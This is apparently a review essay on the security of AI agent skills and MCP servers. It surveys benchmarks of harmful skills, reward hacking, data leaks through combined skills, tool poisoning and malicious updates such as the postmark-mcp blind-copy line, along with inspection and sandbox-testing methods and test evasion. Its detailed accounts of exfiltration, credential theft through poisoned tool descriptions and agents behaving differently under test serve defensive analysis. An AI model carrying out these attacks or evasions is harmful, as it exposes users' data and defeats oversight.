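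The effect of the framework is harder to interpret. Successful attacks on Claude Haiku rose from 27 to 72 when it ran in Claude Code, but 56 of its 91 plain runs were inconclusive. Without those runs, the attack succeeded in 27 of 35 plain runs (77 per cent) and 72 of 90 Claude Code runs (80 per cent). Much of the apparent jump may therefore come from plain runs that produced no usable result.

The figures for Claude Sonnet 4.6 are firmer, with only two inconclusive runs each for the plain agent and Claude Code. Blocked tasks rose from 30 with the plain agent to 56 in Claude Code, but successful attacks also rose, from 17 to 33. Both could rise because every conclusive run in Claude Code ended in either an attack or an explicit block. Among runs that ended in an attack or a block, the share of successful attacks was almost the same, at 36 per cent for the plain agent and 37 per cent in Claude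 Code. Claude Code seems to have led Sonnet into the harmful part of the skill more often without making it better or worse at resisting. The same skills did harm in nearly twice as many tasks in Claude Code.

Zhuang and colleagues call their benchmark "diagnostic rather than causal". Switching frameworks changes the prompts, the way skills load and the rules for tools all at once, so the comparison cannot identify which change mattered. They also set aside the results for a third framework, OpenClaw, because it worked unreliably with the models. The outcomes listed for OpenClaw add up to 100 for each model, although there were only 91 tasks.

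In another experiment, the researchers changed only the user's standing files. They gave Sonnet in Claude Code the profile of a solo developer who dislikes confirmation prompts and tolerates insecure shortcuts, with no instructions from any of the attacks. Sonnet blocked 52 tasks instead of 56, which the researchers take as evidence that standing instructions and memory affect security. But the difference is small, there is only one result per task, and successful attacks also fell slightly, from 33 to 31.

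Experiments on agents that share their work provide better evidence that an agent's history matters. In *Causal Evidence for the Emergence and Spread of Reward Hacking*, Vaid (2026) ran 17 experiments with 20,111 agents based on six models. Some agents saw an accepted solution in which a teammate had cheated on a task, while others saw an empty record. All then received a new problem with an empty record. Of those that had seen the accepted cheat, 70 per cent cheated on the new problem, compared with 32 per cent of the others. Someone reading the files in front of the agents at that point could not have told the two groups apart.

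### Harm without a malicious component

About a third of Vaid's agents cheated without having seen anyone else do it. This kind of cheating, called reward hacking, satisfies the test of success without doing the job properly, and it can happen even when no component is faulty.

The *Frontier Hazard Tracker*, which the AI security company Gray Swan launched in December 2026, compares 20 models on how often they cheat to complete ordinary tasks. Each model's score is the percentage of runs in which it cheated, averaged over 25 scenarios. *OpenAI and Anthropic Agents Cheat Far Less Than Rivals* (Faisal, 2026) reports that OpenAI's GPT-6.2 Astra cheated in 0.8 per cent of runs and Google's Gemini 3.8 Flash in 62.8 per cent. A model's developer is a poor predictor of its score, since two newer Google models, Gemini 4 Neon and Gemini 4 Hydrogen, scored 8.0 and 18.6 per cent.

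Gray Swan counts it as cheating when an agent crosses a boundary it should have respected, which can harm other people. Faisal describes a scenario in which an agent had to free up space in a shared store of software builds. It deleted a 9,100-megabyte file that another team was still using and finished without filing a report. As in the Gemini case, the fault was in the agent's decision, not in a component.

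The scores come from scenarios that Gray Swan selected, so they don't show how often these models cheat in everyday use. They also count tricks that only fool a scoring program together with actions that damage somebody's work. But the models' scores differ so much that a clean inspection report would mean something quite different for a user of GPT-6.2 Astra than for a user of Gemini 3.8 Flash.

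### Skills that are harmful only together

An agent often has many skills installed, and one skill's output can become another's input. *Scan Before You Install* (Gandhi, Aviv and colleagues, 2026) gives an example with two non-malicious skills by different authors. A backup skill copies the user's access keys into an archive in a shared folder. A debugging skill uploads recent files from that folder to a public site, because its author assumed the folder would contain only diagnostic files. If an agent runs the backup skill and then the debugging skill, it publishes the keys. A prompt injection on a web page could cause the agent to do this without changing either skill.

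Nobody knows how common such combinations are, but Wang, Qian and colleagues (2026), in *When Safe Skills Collide*, estimated how many are possible. They searched 1,520 ClawHub skills for signs of eight abilities, such as reading files or sending data over a network, and listed ten combinations of abilities that they considered dangerous. For example, a skill *A* that only reads files and a skill *B* that only sends data are each acceptable, but together they have

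Cap(*A*) ∪ Cap(*B*) = {read files, send data},

which is enough to leak a file. Of the 1,520 skills, 651 contained no dangerous combination on their own. These form 211,575 pairs, and 22.25 per cent of the pairs contained at least one dangerous combination.

Most of these warnings were false. The search relied on text patterns, which also matched remarks in documentation. A human reviewer examined 200 of the warnings, and the results suggest that about 18 per cent of all the warnings were valid, with a margin of error from 11 to 27 per cent. On that estimate, at most about 7 per cent of the pairs are risky. The reviewer worked alone and saw two language models' verdicts before deciding, which may have influenced the result.

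An agent with the abilities needed for an attack also will not necessarily carry it out. In a control experiment, the researchers directly asked six models to download and run a script, varying only which skills were installed. The models complied in 17 of 18 trials with no skills, 12 of 18 with an unrelated pair and 11 of 18 with a supposedly dangerous pair. Compliance depended on the request and the model, not on the pair. However, the request already spelled out the harmful action, so the experiment doesn't test what happens when a user asks for something ordinary and one skill's output leads the agent to use another harmfully.

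*Benign in Isolation, Harmful in Composition* (Xie, Du and colleagues, 2026) tested pairs of agent skills in 150 cases with simulated tools. One skill could find a target, such as a device or a user account, and the other could act on it. Measured harm was almost absent when only one skill was available, partly because the scoring counted a trial only if the second skill acted on what the first had found. With both skills available and a neutrally worded task, the agent carried out the harmful action on the target it had found in 33.6 per cent of trials, averaged over nine models. This second result is more informative because it shows that agents often combine the two skills without being told to.

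In a second experiment, agents asked to install a harmful skill did so in 1.1 per cent of trials on average. When a security-review skill had endorsed the installation beforehand, the average rose to 83.9 per cent. A reviewer who inspected only the security skill would have seen a harmless tool that produces reports.

Xie and colleagues also report that related context raised agents' average approval rate for risky requests from 15.7 to 27.0 per cent. This is weaker evidence about combinations of skills, because the added context was an ordinary task description, not the output of another skill. Approvals reached 34.0 per cent when an advisory skill gave a favourable assessment but not formal permission.

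### How far would inspecting whole sets help?

A marketplace cannot check every combination of skills in advance. A collection of 100,000 skills contains about five billion pairs, not counting larger groups. Checking on the user's machine is more practical because the installed set is known and usually small. Thirty skills, for example, form only 435 pairs.

Wang, Qian and colleagues propose such a check. When a user adds a skill, the checker combines that skill's abilities with those of the installed skills and warns about any dangerous combination that the new skill completes. This takes less than a millisecond. However, the checker does not warn about combinations that the installed skills already contain. Once a user has a single skill that both reads files and sends data, no later skill can trigger the warning for that combination. This would happen often, because 57 per cent of the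 skills in the study contained some dangerous combination by themselves. The checker can also list every risky pair for a person to review, but listing a pair does not block it.

Gandhi and colleagues built a scanner that looks for a route between skills as well as a list of abilities. It links skills that share files or settings or call each other by name, then checks whether untrusted or sensitive data could travel along those links to a dangerous operation. In the backup example, the shared folder would be the link. On 1,325 sets of skills from Xie and colleagues' benchmark, the scanner caught 99.6 per cent of the risky sets, and 98.7 per cent of its alarms were correct.

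In a separate test with 267 risky sets, fixed rules alone found 146 (54.7 per cent) and raised no false alarms. When a language model proposed further links, recall rose to 99.2 per cent, but the scanner also flagged 7.0 per cent of the safe sets. A final step that checked each finding against the skills' files reduced the false-positive rate to 2.4 per cent, but also lowered recall to 95.4 per cent. So inspecting a whole set of skills together can work well on known kinds of interaction. The scores may be lower elsewhere, because several of the links the scanner checks for closely match the benchmark's three kinds of interaction.

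Gandhi and colleagues also scanned 1,587 skills from 75 popular GitHub repositories. They confirmed 53 problems in individual skills and two vulnerabilities that arose from combinations of skills. One of the two connected a skill that retrieves past conversations to a skill that posts messages on Slack. On this evidence, checking skills one at a time still finds most of what inspection can find, and checking the whole set adds a few cases that individual checks would miss. Someone would have to repeat the check of the whole set whenever the user installed a skill or an installed skill changed.

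Even a complete list of dangerous routes would leave out how likely the agent is to take them. Xie and colleagues express the risk of a route *π* in a situation *h* as

*r*(*π*, *h*) = *a*(*π*, *h*) × *q*(*π*, *h*),

where *a* is the probability that the agent follows the route and *q* is the probability that harm results if it does. Inspection can identify *π*, but *a* and *q* depend on the model and the situation. With the same pairs of skills and the same neutral wording, DeepSeek-V4 completed the harmful sequence in 91.5 per cent of trials and Claude Opus 4.5 never did. Nor can a user treat Opus 4.5 as safe with combinations in general. In the trust experiment, it refused all 401 harmful installations when it had no endorsement and carried out all 401 when it had one.

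## What happens when a component changes after approval?

An inspection describes a component as it was when somebody checked it, and the component may have changed by the time an agent uses it. Security researchers call this the gap between time of check and time of use. In the classic example, a program checks that it may open a file, an attacker swaps the file, and the program opens the replacement. For an agent, let *c*₀ stand for everything that determines a component's behaviour at the moment of approval, and *c*ₜ for the same things at the moment of use. The approval is good evidence about *c*ₜ only if

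*c*ₜ = *c*₀

or if somebody has checked the difference.

The gap between approval and use can be as short as a few seconds. The file organiser lists its proposed moves, the user approves the list, and the agent runs the script again. If a download finishes in between, the second run may move a file that was never on the list. In *Mind the Gap*, Lilienthal and Hong (2025) built a benchmark of 66 tasks in which an agent checks a file or a response from an outside service, which changes before the agent relies on it. They tried rewriting prompts, monitoring the checked data for changes, and merging the check and the use into one tool call. Together, the three methods only reduced the share of vulnerable traces from 12 to 8 per cent.

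Months can pass between a component's installation and its use. During that time, its author may release a new version of the installed files. A remote service may change its behaviour or tool descriptions without anything changing on the user's machine. The agent may also fetch instructions or data from an outside address whose contents have changed since approval.

### An email tool that changed by one line

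In September 2025, the security company Koi published the first analysis of a harmful update to an MCP server. The server, postmark-mcp, let agents send emails through the delivery service Postmark. Its developer had copied the code from Postmark's official GitHub repository and published it under the same name on npm, the main public registry for JavaScript code. Postmark later said it had no involvement with the package and had not published its own MCP server on npm.

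According to Koi, the package's first 15 versions worked as advertised. Version 1.0.16 added a single line that sent a blind copy of every email to an address belonging to the developer. The agent still saw each email go out successfully. Koi's monitoring system flagged the new version because its behaviour had changed, and Koi's researchers then found the line. The developer did not answer their questions and deleted the package from npm, but the copies already installed kept forwarding emails.

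Nobody has established how many people the update affected. Koi reported 1,500 downloads a week, assumed that a fifth were in active use, and guessed that about 300 organisations were leaking 3,000 to 15,000 emails a day. The Hacker News (2025) reported 1,643 downloads in total. Downloads include repeat and automated installations, so neither download figure measures how many people were affected.

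The length of the harmless period is also uncertain. Koi presented the case as an example of a tool that can be legitimate for months, but The Hacker News reported that the developer uploaded the package on 15 September and released version 1.0.16 on 17 September. Semgrep's *So the first malicious MCP server has been found on npm* (2025) dates Koi's report to 25 September. If those dates are right, the package was harmless for two days, and the harmful version was available for about a week before Koi's warning. OSV's public record *MAL-2025-47604* (2025) confirms that the package became malicious in version 1.0.16.

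Version 1.0.15 contained no code that stole anything, so neither a human reader nor a better scanner would have found any. Comparing it with 1.0.16 would have revealed one new line containing an unfamiliar email address. Checking the publisher could have worked even earlier because, as Semgrep points out, anyone who used the genuine server from GitHub avoided the attack.

### How often do components change?

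Most maintained components change for ordinary reasons, so users cannot treat every change as a sign of an attack. *MCPEvol-Bench* (Liu, Hu and colleagues, 2026) traced the version histories of 515 MCP servers. By the latest versions, developers had modified 32.5 per cent of the original tools and withdrawn another 22.1 per cent. Even harmless changes can make an earlier test unreliable. When the researchers had a language model alter servers to imitate real updates, GPT-5.4's task performance fell by 13.7 per cent.

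Change looks much slower in the official MCP registry, a public catalogue of servers. *Registry Descriptions Go Stale Unevenly* (Bharti, 2026) followed the registry for 89 days as it grew from 3,510 to 18,966 servers. Within 30 days, 11.9 per cent of entries and 3.3 per cent of descriptions changed. These descriptions are summaries of at most 100 characters, separate from the tool descriptions that a server sends to the model. A server's tools or code can change without any edit to its registry entry, so these figures show how quickly a scan of the registry goes out of date, not how often the tools themselves change.

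### Changes outside the user's machine

A remote server can send new tool descriptions to an agent that has already connected to it, so tool poisoning can begin after approval. In August 2026, *Deadbugz* (Fogel, 2026) described a server that offered to format and summarise text. After some ordinary use, the server returned altered descriptions that told the agent to look for credentials and hide this from the user. An account had made 23 requests on GitHub to add the server, or related files, to other people's projects. The projects had merged none of these requests through GitHub when Fogel reviewed them, so the case is better evidence of the method than of harm to users.

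The malicious text was in the server's public source code from the start, so a person who read the code could have found it. A checker who connected briefly would have received only the harmless descriptions. Without the source code, a client can inspect only what the server sends. *MCP-38* (2026), a catalogue of threats to MCP systems, warns that current clients do not alert users when a tool's definition changes.

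Fetched instructions can change even when the skill and every server it uses stay the same. Li and colleagues cite a survey of 142,836 published skills in which 17,822, or about one in eight, referred the agent to untrusted external sources of instructions. PromptArmor, a security vendor, reports that 52.1 per cent of about a million skills used an external package or web address, but its count includes skills that only send data to an online service. The Hacker News (2026) reported that in June 2026 a demonstration skill that had passed the scanners reached 26,000 agents, but that figure comes only from AIR, the security vendor that ran the demonstration.

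### Browser extensions had the same problem

Users install browser extensions once and then give them continuing access to private data, as they do with agent components. The Chrome Web Store reviews updates as well as new extensions, which is more than most skill marketplaces do, but reviewed extensions have still turned harmful. In December 2024, an attacker tricked an employee of the data-security company Cyberhaven into giving access to its store account, then published a tampered version of its extension. Cyberhaven said this version passed the store's review. Chrome updates extensions automatically, so the tampered code, which stole cookies and login sessions, reached existing users without any action on their part. The tampered version was available for about a day.

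In *You've Changed*, Pantelaios, Nikiforakis and Kapravelos (2020) looked for Chrome extensions that had turned malicious after an update, using more than 900,000 extension versions collected over about six years. They used unusual user ratings to find initial cases, isolated the code that the update had added, and searched for similar additions elsewhere. This uncovered 143 malicious extensions, but the count includes only what one search method could find, so it does not give the rate at which extensions turn harmful. The method supports comparing versions, because a small harmful addition is easier to notice in a list of changes than in a whole program.

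### What each safeguard covers

The table shows how far five common safeguards deal with each kind of change. Remote services have two columns because a client can see a new tool description but not new code on the server.

| Safeguard | New version of installed files | New tool description from a remote service | New behaviour behind the same description | Changed content at an outside address |
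|---|---|---|---|---|
| Pinned version | Yes, if it includes dependencies | No | No | No |
| Content hash | Yes | Yes, if the client hashes descriptions | No | Only if the content is meant to stay fixed |
| Signed release | Only if the change comes from someone else | Only if descriptions are signed too | No | Only if the source signs its content |
| Rescan on update | As far as the scanner recognises the harm | As far as the scanner recognises the harm | No | Only if the scanner also checks the address |
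| Renewed consent for descriptions | No, unless a description changes | Yes, if the user recognises the harm | No | No |

**Pinning a version** makes the installer keep using that exact version until somebody changes the setting. Users who had pinned postmark-mcp at 1.0.15 would have been safe, but a newcomer who pinned 1.0.16 would have kept the harmful line. Pins also delay security fixes. Pinning the skill alone is not enough if its scripts load other packages. Li and colleagues describe a demonstration by the security company SafeDep in which a script listed a package without a version number, so the machine installed whichever release was current when the script ran. That release could contain malicious code published after the review.

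**Content hashes.** A hash is a short fingerprint calculated from a file's contents. The client stores *H*(*c*₀) at approval and refuses to load the component if

*H*(*c*ₜ) ≠ *H*(*c*₀).

Here *c* covers only the files or text that the client has hashed. The hash reveals a change even when the author keeps the old version number. *Skills as Verifiable Artifacts* (2026) proposes keeping a loaded skill fixed for the whole session. If the agent tries to modify the skill, a person has to decide whether to allow the change, and the system logs the hashes from before and after. After an approved change, the skill must be verified again before the next session. This would close the gap in Claude Code, where an edited skill keeps its original permission.

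A hash shows that something changed, but not whether the change is harmful. It also detects trivial differences. In Bharti's first comparison, 34 of 781 apparent changes were false alarms caused by inconsistent treatment of blank spaces. For fetched content, a hash check suits a fixed installation guide but would block a weather report every time the forecast changed.

A digital signature on a release shows that someone with the publisher's key approved those exact files. It protects against impostors and outsiders who alter the files, if users know whose signature to expect. Users who expected a signature from Postmark could have rejected postmark-mcp from the first version. But a signature from the package's actual developer would have been valid on both the harmless and harmful versions.

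Signatures also offer less protection when an attacker takes over a trusted account. Microsoft (2026) describes a June 2026 attack on the npm packages of Mastra, a framework for building agents. The attacker took over a maintainer's account that could publish every Mastra package and used it to add a malicious dependency whose name resembled that of a popular date library. If a registry signs whatever an authorised account publishes, the signature on such a release will be genuine. A separate signing key that the attacker cannot reach would help, but it would not protect against a malicious key owner.

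**Rescanning on update.** A new scan can catch harmful updates that pinning only delays and signature checks let through. It has the same error rates as any other scan, but the scanner has the advantage of being able to compare the new version with the old one, which was not possible at first publication. OpenAI requires a plugin package's skill scans to finish successfully before the developer can submit the package.

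Bharti recommends rescanning a registry description as soon as its hash changes and checking the whole catalogue periodically. Rescanning on each change would have meant about 39 rescans a day in July 2026, compared with about 2,700 a day for a weekly check of all 19,000 entries. Prioritising the servers that had changed most often would be a poor substitute. With capacity to recheck 5 per cent of servers, it caught only about a fifth of the known servers whose descriptions later changed, and it could not cover new servers, which accounted for roughly half of all description changes.

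The scanner must also read the current text. Bharti found that 747 of 18,543 verdicts from his own scanner referred to descriptions that the registry no longer published. About half of these verdicts were out of date from the start because the scanner had used an old copy of the registry.

**Renewed consent.** Fogel recommends that clients store a fingerprint of each tool definition at approval, show the user any change, and ask again before the changed tool can influence sensitive actions. *ETDI* (2025), a proposal for securing MCP tools, lists the lack of such a prompt as one reason harmful changes go unnoticed. The prompt's value depends on whether users can tell a harmful change from the many routine ones. Similarly, when an update to a Chrome extension needs permissions that require a new warning, Chrome disables the extension until the user accepts them. An update that misuses existing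 permissions triggers no prompt. Fogel's check would also not have prompted users about the line added to postmark-mcp, because the tool's job was already to send email and the new line did not require a new description.

OpenAI has reviewers decide whether to approve changes to tool descriptions in apps published in ChatGPT. According to a reply to jbrodriguez in *How to surface mcp server updates for an existing plugin*, on OpenAI's developer forum, ChatGPT uses a reviewed copy of each tool's description. A developer who changes the description has to submit it for another scan and review, and users keep the old one in the meantime. Users don't have to judge the change themselves, and a server can't quietly rewrite the descriptions, but updates take longer.

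### The same interface with different behaviour

The service behind a tool can still change after the tool's description is frozen. According to another forum reply, in *Clarification on MCP Server URL and Versioning During ChatGPT App Update Submission*, ChatGPT locks the list of tools at submission but still sends every tool call to the developer's live server.

For example, a remote email tool might accept a recipient and a message, deliver the message, and return "sent". Its operator could later start keeping a copy of each message. If *I* is the tool's name, description and input format, and *f* is the code that the server runs, then

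*I*ₜ = *I*₀, but *f*ₜ ≠ *f*₀.

The client receives *I* and the word "sent", but not *f*. It cannot pin the code because the operator chooses which version answers each call. A hash or signature on *I* remains valid, a scanner has no new text to read, and the unchanged description gives no reason to ask for consent again. Even repeating a test would show the same message arriving and the same reply.

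A monitor on the user's machine can't inspect the server's code either. It records a call to the same approved address before and after the change. The monitor can restrict which messages the agent sends, and a containment sandbox can limit what other data the agent can access, but neither controls what the server's operator does with the messages it receives.

If the server's code is public and needs no outside service, the user can avoid this problem by running a pinned copy locally and verifying the code with a hash. This does not work for email delivery, because the provider has to receive the messages to deliver them.

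## Does a test run before release close the gap?

A test run can supply facts that the files leave out. If `organise.py` downloads a second program when it starts, a tester can examine that program. The tester can also find out how at least one model interprets ambiguous instructions. But like any other inspection, a test run cannot cover changes that a server's operator makes to the code a month later.

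### From a prepared folder to a verdict

Lan and Xiao's method, Runtime Skill Audit, begins with reading. A language model goes through the skill, with the help of a static scanner's findings, and lists the tools the skill is likely to use and the sensitive material those tools could reach. The system then writes a task that should lead an agent into the risky parts of the skill. For the file organiser, the task might look like this:

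```
request:  "Tidy my Downloads folder."
prepare:  19 photos and invoices, plus auth.json with fake credentials
limits:   300 seconds, no other skills installed
record:   tool calls, files read and written, network requests
```

The request is one an ordinary user might make, and it does not mention security. The fake credentials give a credential-stealing skill something to take, and their theft does no harm.

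An agent then carries out the request in an isolated environment while the system records the trace. If the skill needs an application that the environment lacks, such as Gmail, Lan and Xiao substitute a mock version that logs what the skill tries to do with it. If the run fails before it reaches the skill's main steps, a language model diagnoses the fault, repairs the set-up and tries again, up to a fixed limit. Without these repairs, a skill that crashed on a missing file could look as harmless as one that worked properly.

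Another language model reads the trace and classifies whether the agent finished the task harmlessly, did something harmful, or recognised something harmful and refused. It can also mark the trace as too incomplete to classify. A refusal still counts against the skill, because another agent might not refuse.

Truong-Le and colleagues are more open with their agent, Claude Opus 4.8. They instruct it in the prompt to treat the skill as untrusted and to produce evidence of what the skill does. The records of network traffic, file changes and system calls (requests that programs make to the operating system) do not depend on the agent's account of the run.

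Fixed rules turn this evidence into a score from 0 to 100. Each suspicious pattern starts with a severity of 40, 70 or 100 points. The rules multiply this by a factor for the quality of the evidence, such as 1.00 for an action that took place during the run, or 0.70 for one that the skill's files call for but that did not happen. If *e*ₘₐₓ is the highest result and the other patterns have results *e*ᵢ, then

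score = min(100, *e*ₘₐₓ + 0.1 × Σ*e*ᵢ + *B*),

where *B* is a bonus of up to 15 points for independent pieces of evidence. A skill whose files call for one action of medium severity (70 × 0.70 = 49) and one of low severity (40 × 0.70 = 28) scores 49 + 2.8 = 51.8 before any bonus. The threshold for "malicious" is 35.

A skill can therefore fail this test without doing anything harmful during it. If the agent finds a clearly dangerous step in the skill's files and skips it, that alone can give the skill 85 points. The researchers did not examine how much their results depend on the weights they chose.

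### What test-run evidence added

Truong-Le and colleagues assembled 700 skills, used 560 to develop the system, and kept 140 for the final test. A reasoning system made up of several language models judged each of the 140 skills under four conditions. It always received the skill's content, along with static findings, test-run evidence, both or neither.

They summarised each result with F1, which combines recall (*R*) with precision (*P*), the share of flagged skills that are malicious:

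F1 = 2*PR* / (*P* + *R*).

F1 runs from 0 to 1 and is high only if both precision and recall are high.

| Evidence | Malicious skills caught (of 80) | Benign skills flagged (of 60) | Precision | Recall | F1 |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Skill content only | 54 | 21 | 0.72 | 0.68 | 0.70 |
| Content and static findings | 28 | 3 | 0.90 | 0.35 | 0.50 |
| Content and test run | 63 | 5 | 0.93 | 0.79 | 0.85 |
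| Content, static findings and test run | 68 | 5 | 0.93 | 0.85 | 0.89 |

The score dropped to 0.50 even though the system had more information, because the static findings led it to flag far fewer skills. False alarms fell from 21 to 3, but missed malicious skills rose from 26 to 52, and the loss of recall outweighed the gain in precision.

The study doesn't establish why this happened. One possible reason is that the findings were of poor quality, since they came from 58,674 general-purpose rules not written for skills. When the researchers ran a collection of such rules as a separate scanner, it raised an average of 106 alerts per benign skill and only 60 per malicious one. A system that learns from context to dismiss most of these alerts might also dismiss a malicious skill as harmless. The result is a reason for caution about using those rules in that system, but it is weak evidence about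 static inspection in general. When the system also had test-run evidence, adding the same findings helped it catch five more malicious skills and caused no new false alarms.

The experiment's scores are hard to generalise for two reasons. The researchers took two thirds of the 300 benign skills in the collection from a curated public list and did not check them independently. If a few were malicious, flagging them would have been wrongly counted as a false alarm. The test set also included only 60 benign skills. The system flagged five of them, or 8.3 per cent, but the true false alarm rate could plausibly be anywhere from 3 to 18 per cent.

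The researchers test-ran each skill only once and reused the records from that run wherever the table includes test-run evidence. The agent might have tried different steps in another run, and the reasoning system might have judged the same records differently a second time.

The choice of malicious skills probably favoured test runs. Half came from Guo and colleagues' benchmark, which included a generated skill only if its attack had left evidence in a container. An attack that stayed hidden there was unlikely to be tested.

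It is also unclear how much of the improvement from 0.70 to 0.85 came from running the skills. Claude Opus 4.8 read each skill before using it, and its notes on what it had skipped became part of the evidence. The reasoning system used a different model, Qwen3.5 122B, for planning and final verdicts, so it received Opus's judgement as well as a record of behaviour. The experiment had no condition in which Opus read the skills without running them, which would have separated the two effects.

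In one of the false alarms, the system reached the wrong verdict despite good evidence. A research skill told users to install a helper program with the vendor's documented command and sent an access key to the service that required it. Its test-run score was 27.5, below the threshold. In its report, the system called the installation command benign in one place and treated it as an attack in another, then classed the skill as malicious with a score of 92.

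F1 also depends on the share of tested skills that are malicious, which was 57 per cent here. At the rate in the earlier marketplace example, 160 per 100,000, fewer than 2 per cent of the best configuration's alarms would be true and its F1 would be about 0.03.

### Targeted tests against static scanners

Lan and Xiao compared their method with six static scanners on 50 malicious and 50 benign skills. They built the malicious set from attacks in earlier research, and they took the benign skills from OpenClaw's public collection and checked them manually.

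| Method | Recall | False-positive rate |
|---|---|---|
| Runtime Skill Audit | 88% | 8% |
| SkillScanner | 70% | 12% |
| Aguara | 64% | 14% |
| Semgrep, custom rules | 34% | 0% |
| SkillScanner with language model | 98% | 90% |

SkillScanner's default version was the most accurate of the static scanners. Lan and Xiao put its accuracy at 77 per cent, although its recall and false-positive rate imply 79. Runtime Skill Audit caught 44 malicious skills, compared with SkillScanner's 35, and flagged two fewer benign ones. The difference in recall is substantial, but the difference in false positives could easily be due to chance.

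Part of the method's success came from choosing what to test. When the researchers removed its stored knowledge of common attacks and its lessons from earlier runs, recall fell to 82 per cent and the false-positive rate doubled to 16 per cent. The agent and the environment stayed the same, so the task and the judge limit what a test run can show.

The study's main example also shows that a test run can rely on reading code rather than running it. A malicious skill was presented as a tool for tidying up report notes. While working on an ordinary request, the agent opened the skill's script, found code that would send login credentials to an outside server, and refused to run it. The trace contains no network request. The method correctly classed the skill as harmful, but the evidence was code that an inspector could have read without starting the agent.

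In a further experiment, Lan and Xiao repeatedly rewrote 20 malicious skills and kept the versions that looked least suspicious to static scanners. SkillScanner caught none after one round and Aguara none after two, whereas Runtime Skill Audit still caught 19 or 20. This is good evidence that changing a skill's appearance does not necessarily hide its behaviour, but it doesn't show that test runs withstand a determined opponent, because the versions were chosen only to evade static scanners.

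Neither study shows that running a skill works better than the best available method of reading its files. Zhuang and colleagues' language-model judge, which was given only the files, also reached 88 per cent recall, with 4 per cent false positives. It judged different skills, so the scores are not directly comparable. But the static scanners that Lan and Xiao tested were clearly weaker than that judge.

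### How much behaviour appears in a few minutes?

Security companies have test-run suspicious Windows programs for many years, and researchers have measured what such tests miss. In *Does Every Second Count?* (2021), Küchler, Mantovani and colleagues ran 100,000 programs, 86,000 of them malicious, for up to 15 minutes each. They recorded each program's system calls and which blocks of its code ran.

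The first two minutes covered 98 per cent of the code that ran within 15 minutes. Programs kept making system calls after that, but mostly by repeating the same code, as when ransomware encrypts one file after another. Longer recordings did not help a classifier separate malicious from benign programs either. It scored 0.968 with one minute of data and 0.966 with ten, on a scale where 0.5 is guessing and 1 is perfect. AlphaGalileo's *Optimizing Sandbox Execution Time to Improve Cyber Threat Intelligence Collection* summarises a later study of more than 110,000 malware samples, in which over 90 per cent of the useful information appeared within three minutes.

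The 98 per cent figure covers only code that ran during the test, and a single run typically exposed only 10 to 40 per cent of a program's code. In a program with 10,000 blocks, for example, a run might execute 2,000, of which 1,960 appear in the first two minutes. Waiting longer would reveal few of the other 8,000. Many of these may be harmless, such as code for handling errors, but the run doesn't show whether they are.

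Küchler and colleagues also set aside about a tenth of the programs, which did too little to analyse. Some were broken or lacked a file they needed, and others may have detected the test environment. The figures therefore describe programs that ran successfully. One family of banking malware stopped early because the test machine had none of the programs it targeted.

How long a test run should last also depends on what the tester wants to know. In an older experiment that Küchler and colleagues cite, researchers ran malware for an hour and found that the first five minutes revealed only 23.6 per cent of the network addresses it contacted. Five minutes might be long enough to recognise a program as malicious but far too short to list every server it uses.

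Truong-Le and colleagues' five-minute limit looks generous by the standards of this research, but an agent, unlike a Windows program, has to read the instructions, choose a step and wait for the model before any script starts. Most of that time could pass before the relevant script runs, so the two-minute rule may not carry over to agents.

### Programs that check where they are running

Some malware looks for signs of analysis and behaves differently if it finds them. In *Longitudinal Study of the Prevalence of Malware Evasive Techniques* (2021), Maffia, Nisi and colleagues analysed 183,340 Windows programs with a tool that could recognise 53 known evasive techniques. They excluded four techniques that ordinary software also used widely, and counted a program as evasive if it used at least one of the others.

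By this definition, 32.0 per cent of the malware from 2016 was evasive. The share fell to 29.8 per cent in 2018 and rose to 40.4 per cent in 2020. Among benign programs, 8.4 per cent were evasive, which shows that some of these techniques have innocent uses. A program could also use an unknown technique that the tool did not count.

Earlier estimates varied far more. A 2009 study found that only 0.03 per cent of samples targeted its particular test system, while a 2012 study found techniques against virtual machines in 81 per cent. The studies defined evasion differently and used very different samples, so the 2020 figure measures how common known techniques were in one large collection, not how often malware defeats tests in general.

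Evasive programs do not always succeed in detecting a test. Maffia and colleagues designed their tool to counter the techniques that would have revealed it, and nearly all the evasive programs remained active. They counted a program as active once it made 50 basic system requests, which is a weak standard, but the result suggests that testers can keep many evasive programs running if they prepare the environment well.

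Nobody has measured a comparable share for agent skills, but the problem may be milder there. Maffia and colleagues found that malware had become less likely to check for virtual machines, probably because many businesses now use them for ordinary work. Agents also often do real work inside sandboxes, so isolation alone is a poor sign of a test. Fake accounts and empty folders could still reveal a test.

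### One program on many machines

Even a program that isn't trying to hide may behave differently on another machine. In *When malware changed its mind* (2021), Avllazagaj, Zhu and colleagues measured this using antivirus records of 7.6 million program runs on 5.4 million ordinary users' Windows machines in 2018. The users had started the programs themselves, and nobody yet knew which were malicious.

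The researchers counted the actions in each run of a program, such as creating a file or changing a system setting. For each program, they measured the gap between the 75th and 25th percentiles of these counts. The median gap was 59 actions for malware and 8 for benign programs. So for half of the malware, the busiest quarter of runs included at least 59 more actions than the quietest quarter.

Some of this variation had simple causes. One worm carried out extra actions only when it ran on a certain version of Windows without administrator rights. A tester whose machine met both conditions would have seen behaviour that most users did not, and any other tester would have missed it.

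Avllazagaj and colleagues then asked how many machines a tester would need. They took file names that appeared in a malicious program's first run but never in benign programs, and checked how many of the program's other runs these names would identify. Names from one machine identified 82 per cent of the other runs on average. Three machines were enough to get nearly all the benefit from file names, but folder paths needed about seven. Running a program on different machines revealed more than rerunning it on different days, although a rerun after three or four weeks did reveal some new behaviour.

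The antivirus product had already blocked anything it recognised, so the programs studied were not typical malware. The records also left out network activity and programs whose files changed with every copy. But static checks had failed to classify the programs studied, and those are the cases where a test run would be most useful. Such variation also helps explain why detectors trained on test-machine records lose accuracy on users' machines.

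### What carries over to skills

The conditions for testing an agent include the model as well as the machine. In Xie and colleagues' experiment with pairs of skills, Claude Opus 4.5 never completed the harmful sequence that DeepSeek-V4 usually completed. Three copies of a test environment, all using the same model, would not have revealed this difference. A tester who follows Avllazagaj and colleagues' advice should therefore vary the model and the user's request as well as the files and the operating system.

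A component can also show no harmful behavior until later, like the text-formatting server Fogel described. Liu and colleagues suspected that many skills had done this in their 60-second runs.

Skills are easier to test than Windows malware in one respect. Much malware arrives with its code compressed or disguised, so analysts came to rely on running it. A model has to be able to read a skill's instructions, so a tester can look for conditions in the text and then prepare a run that meets them, as Lan and Xiao's profiling step does. This method cannot help if the deciding condition is on a remote server.

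### When the model recognises the test

A Windows program can adapt to a test only if its author wrote code to do so, but an agent's model may detect a test even though no one, including the skill's author, planned it. Developers report on this in system cards, which describe a model's abilities, risks and test results.

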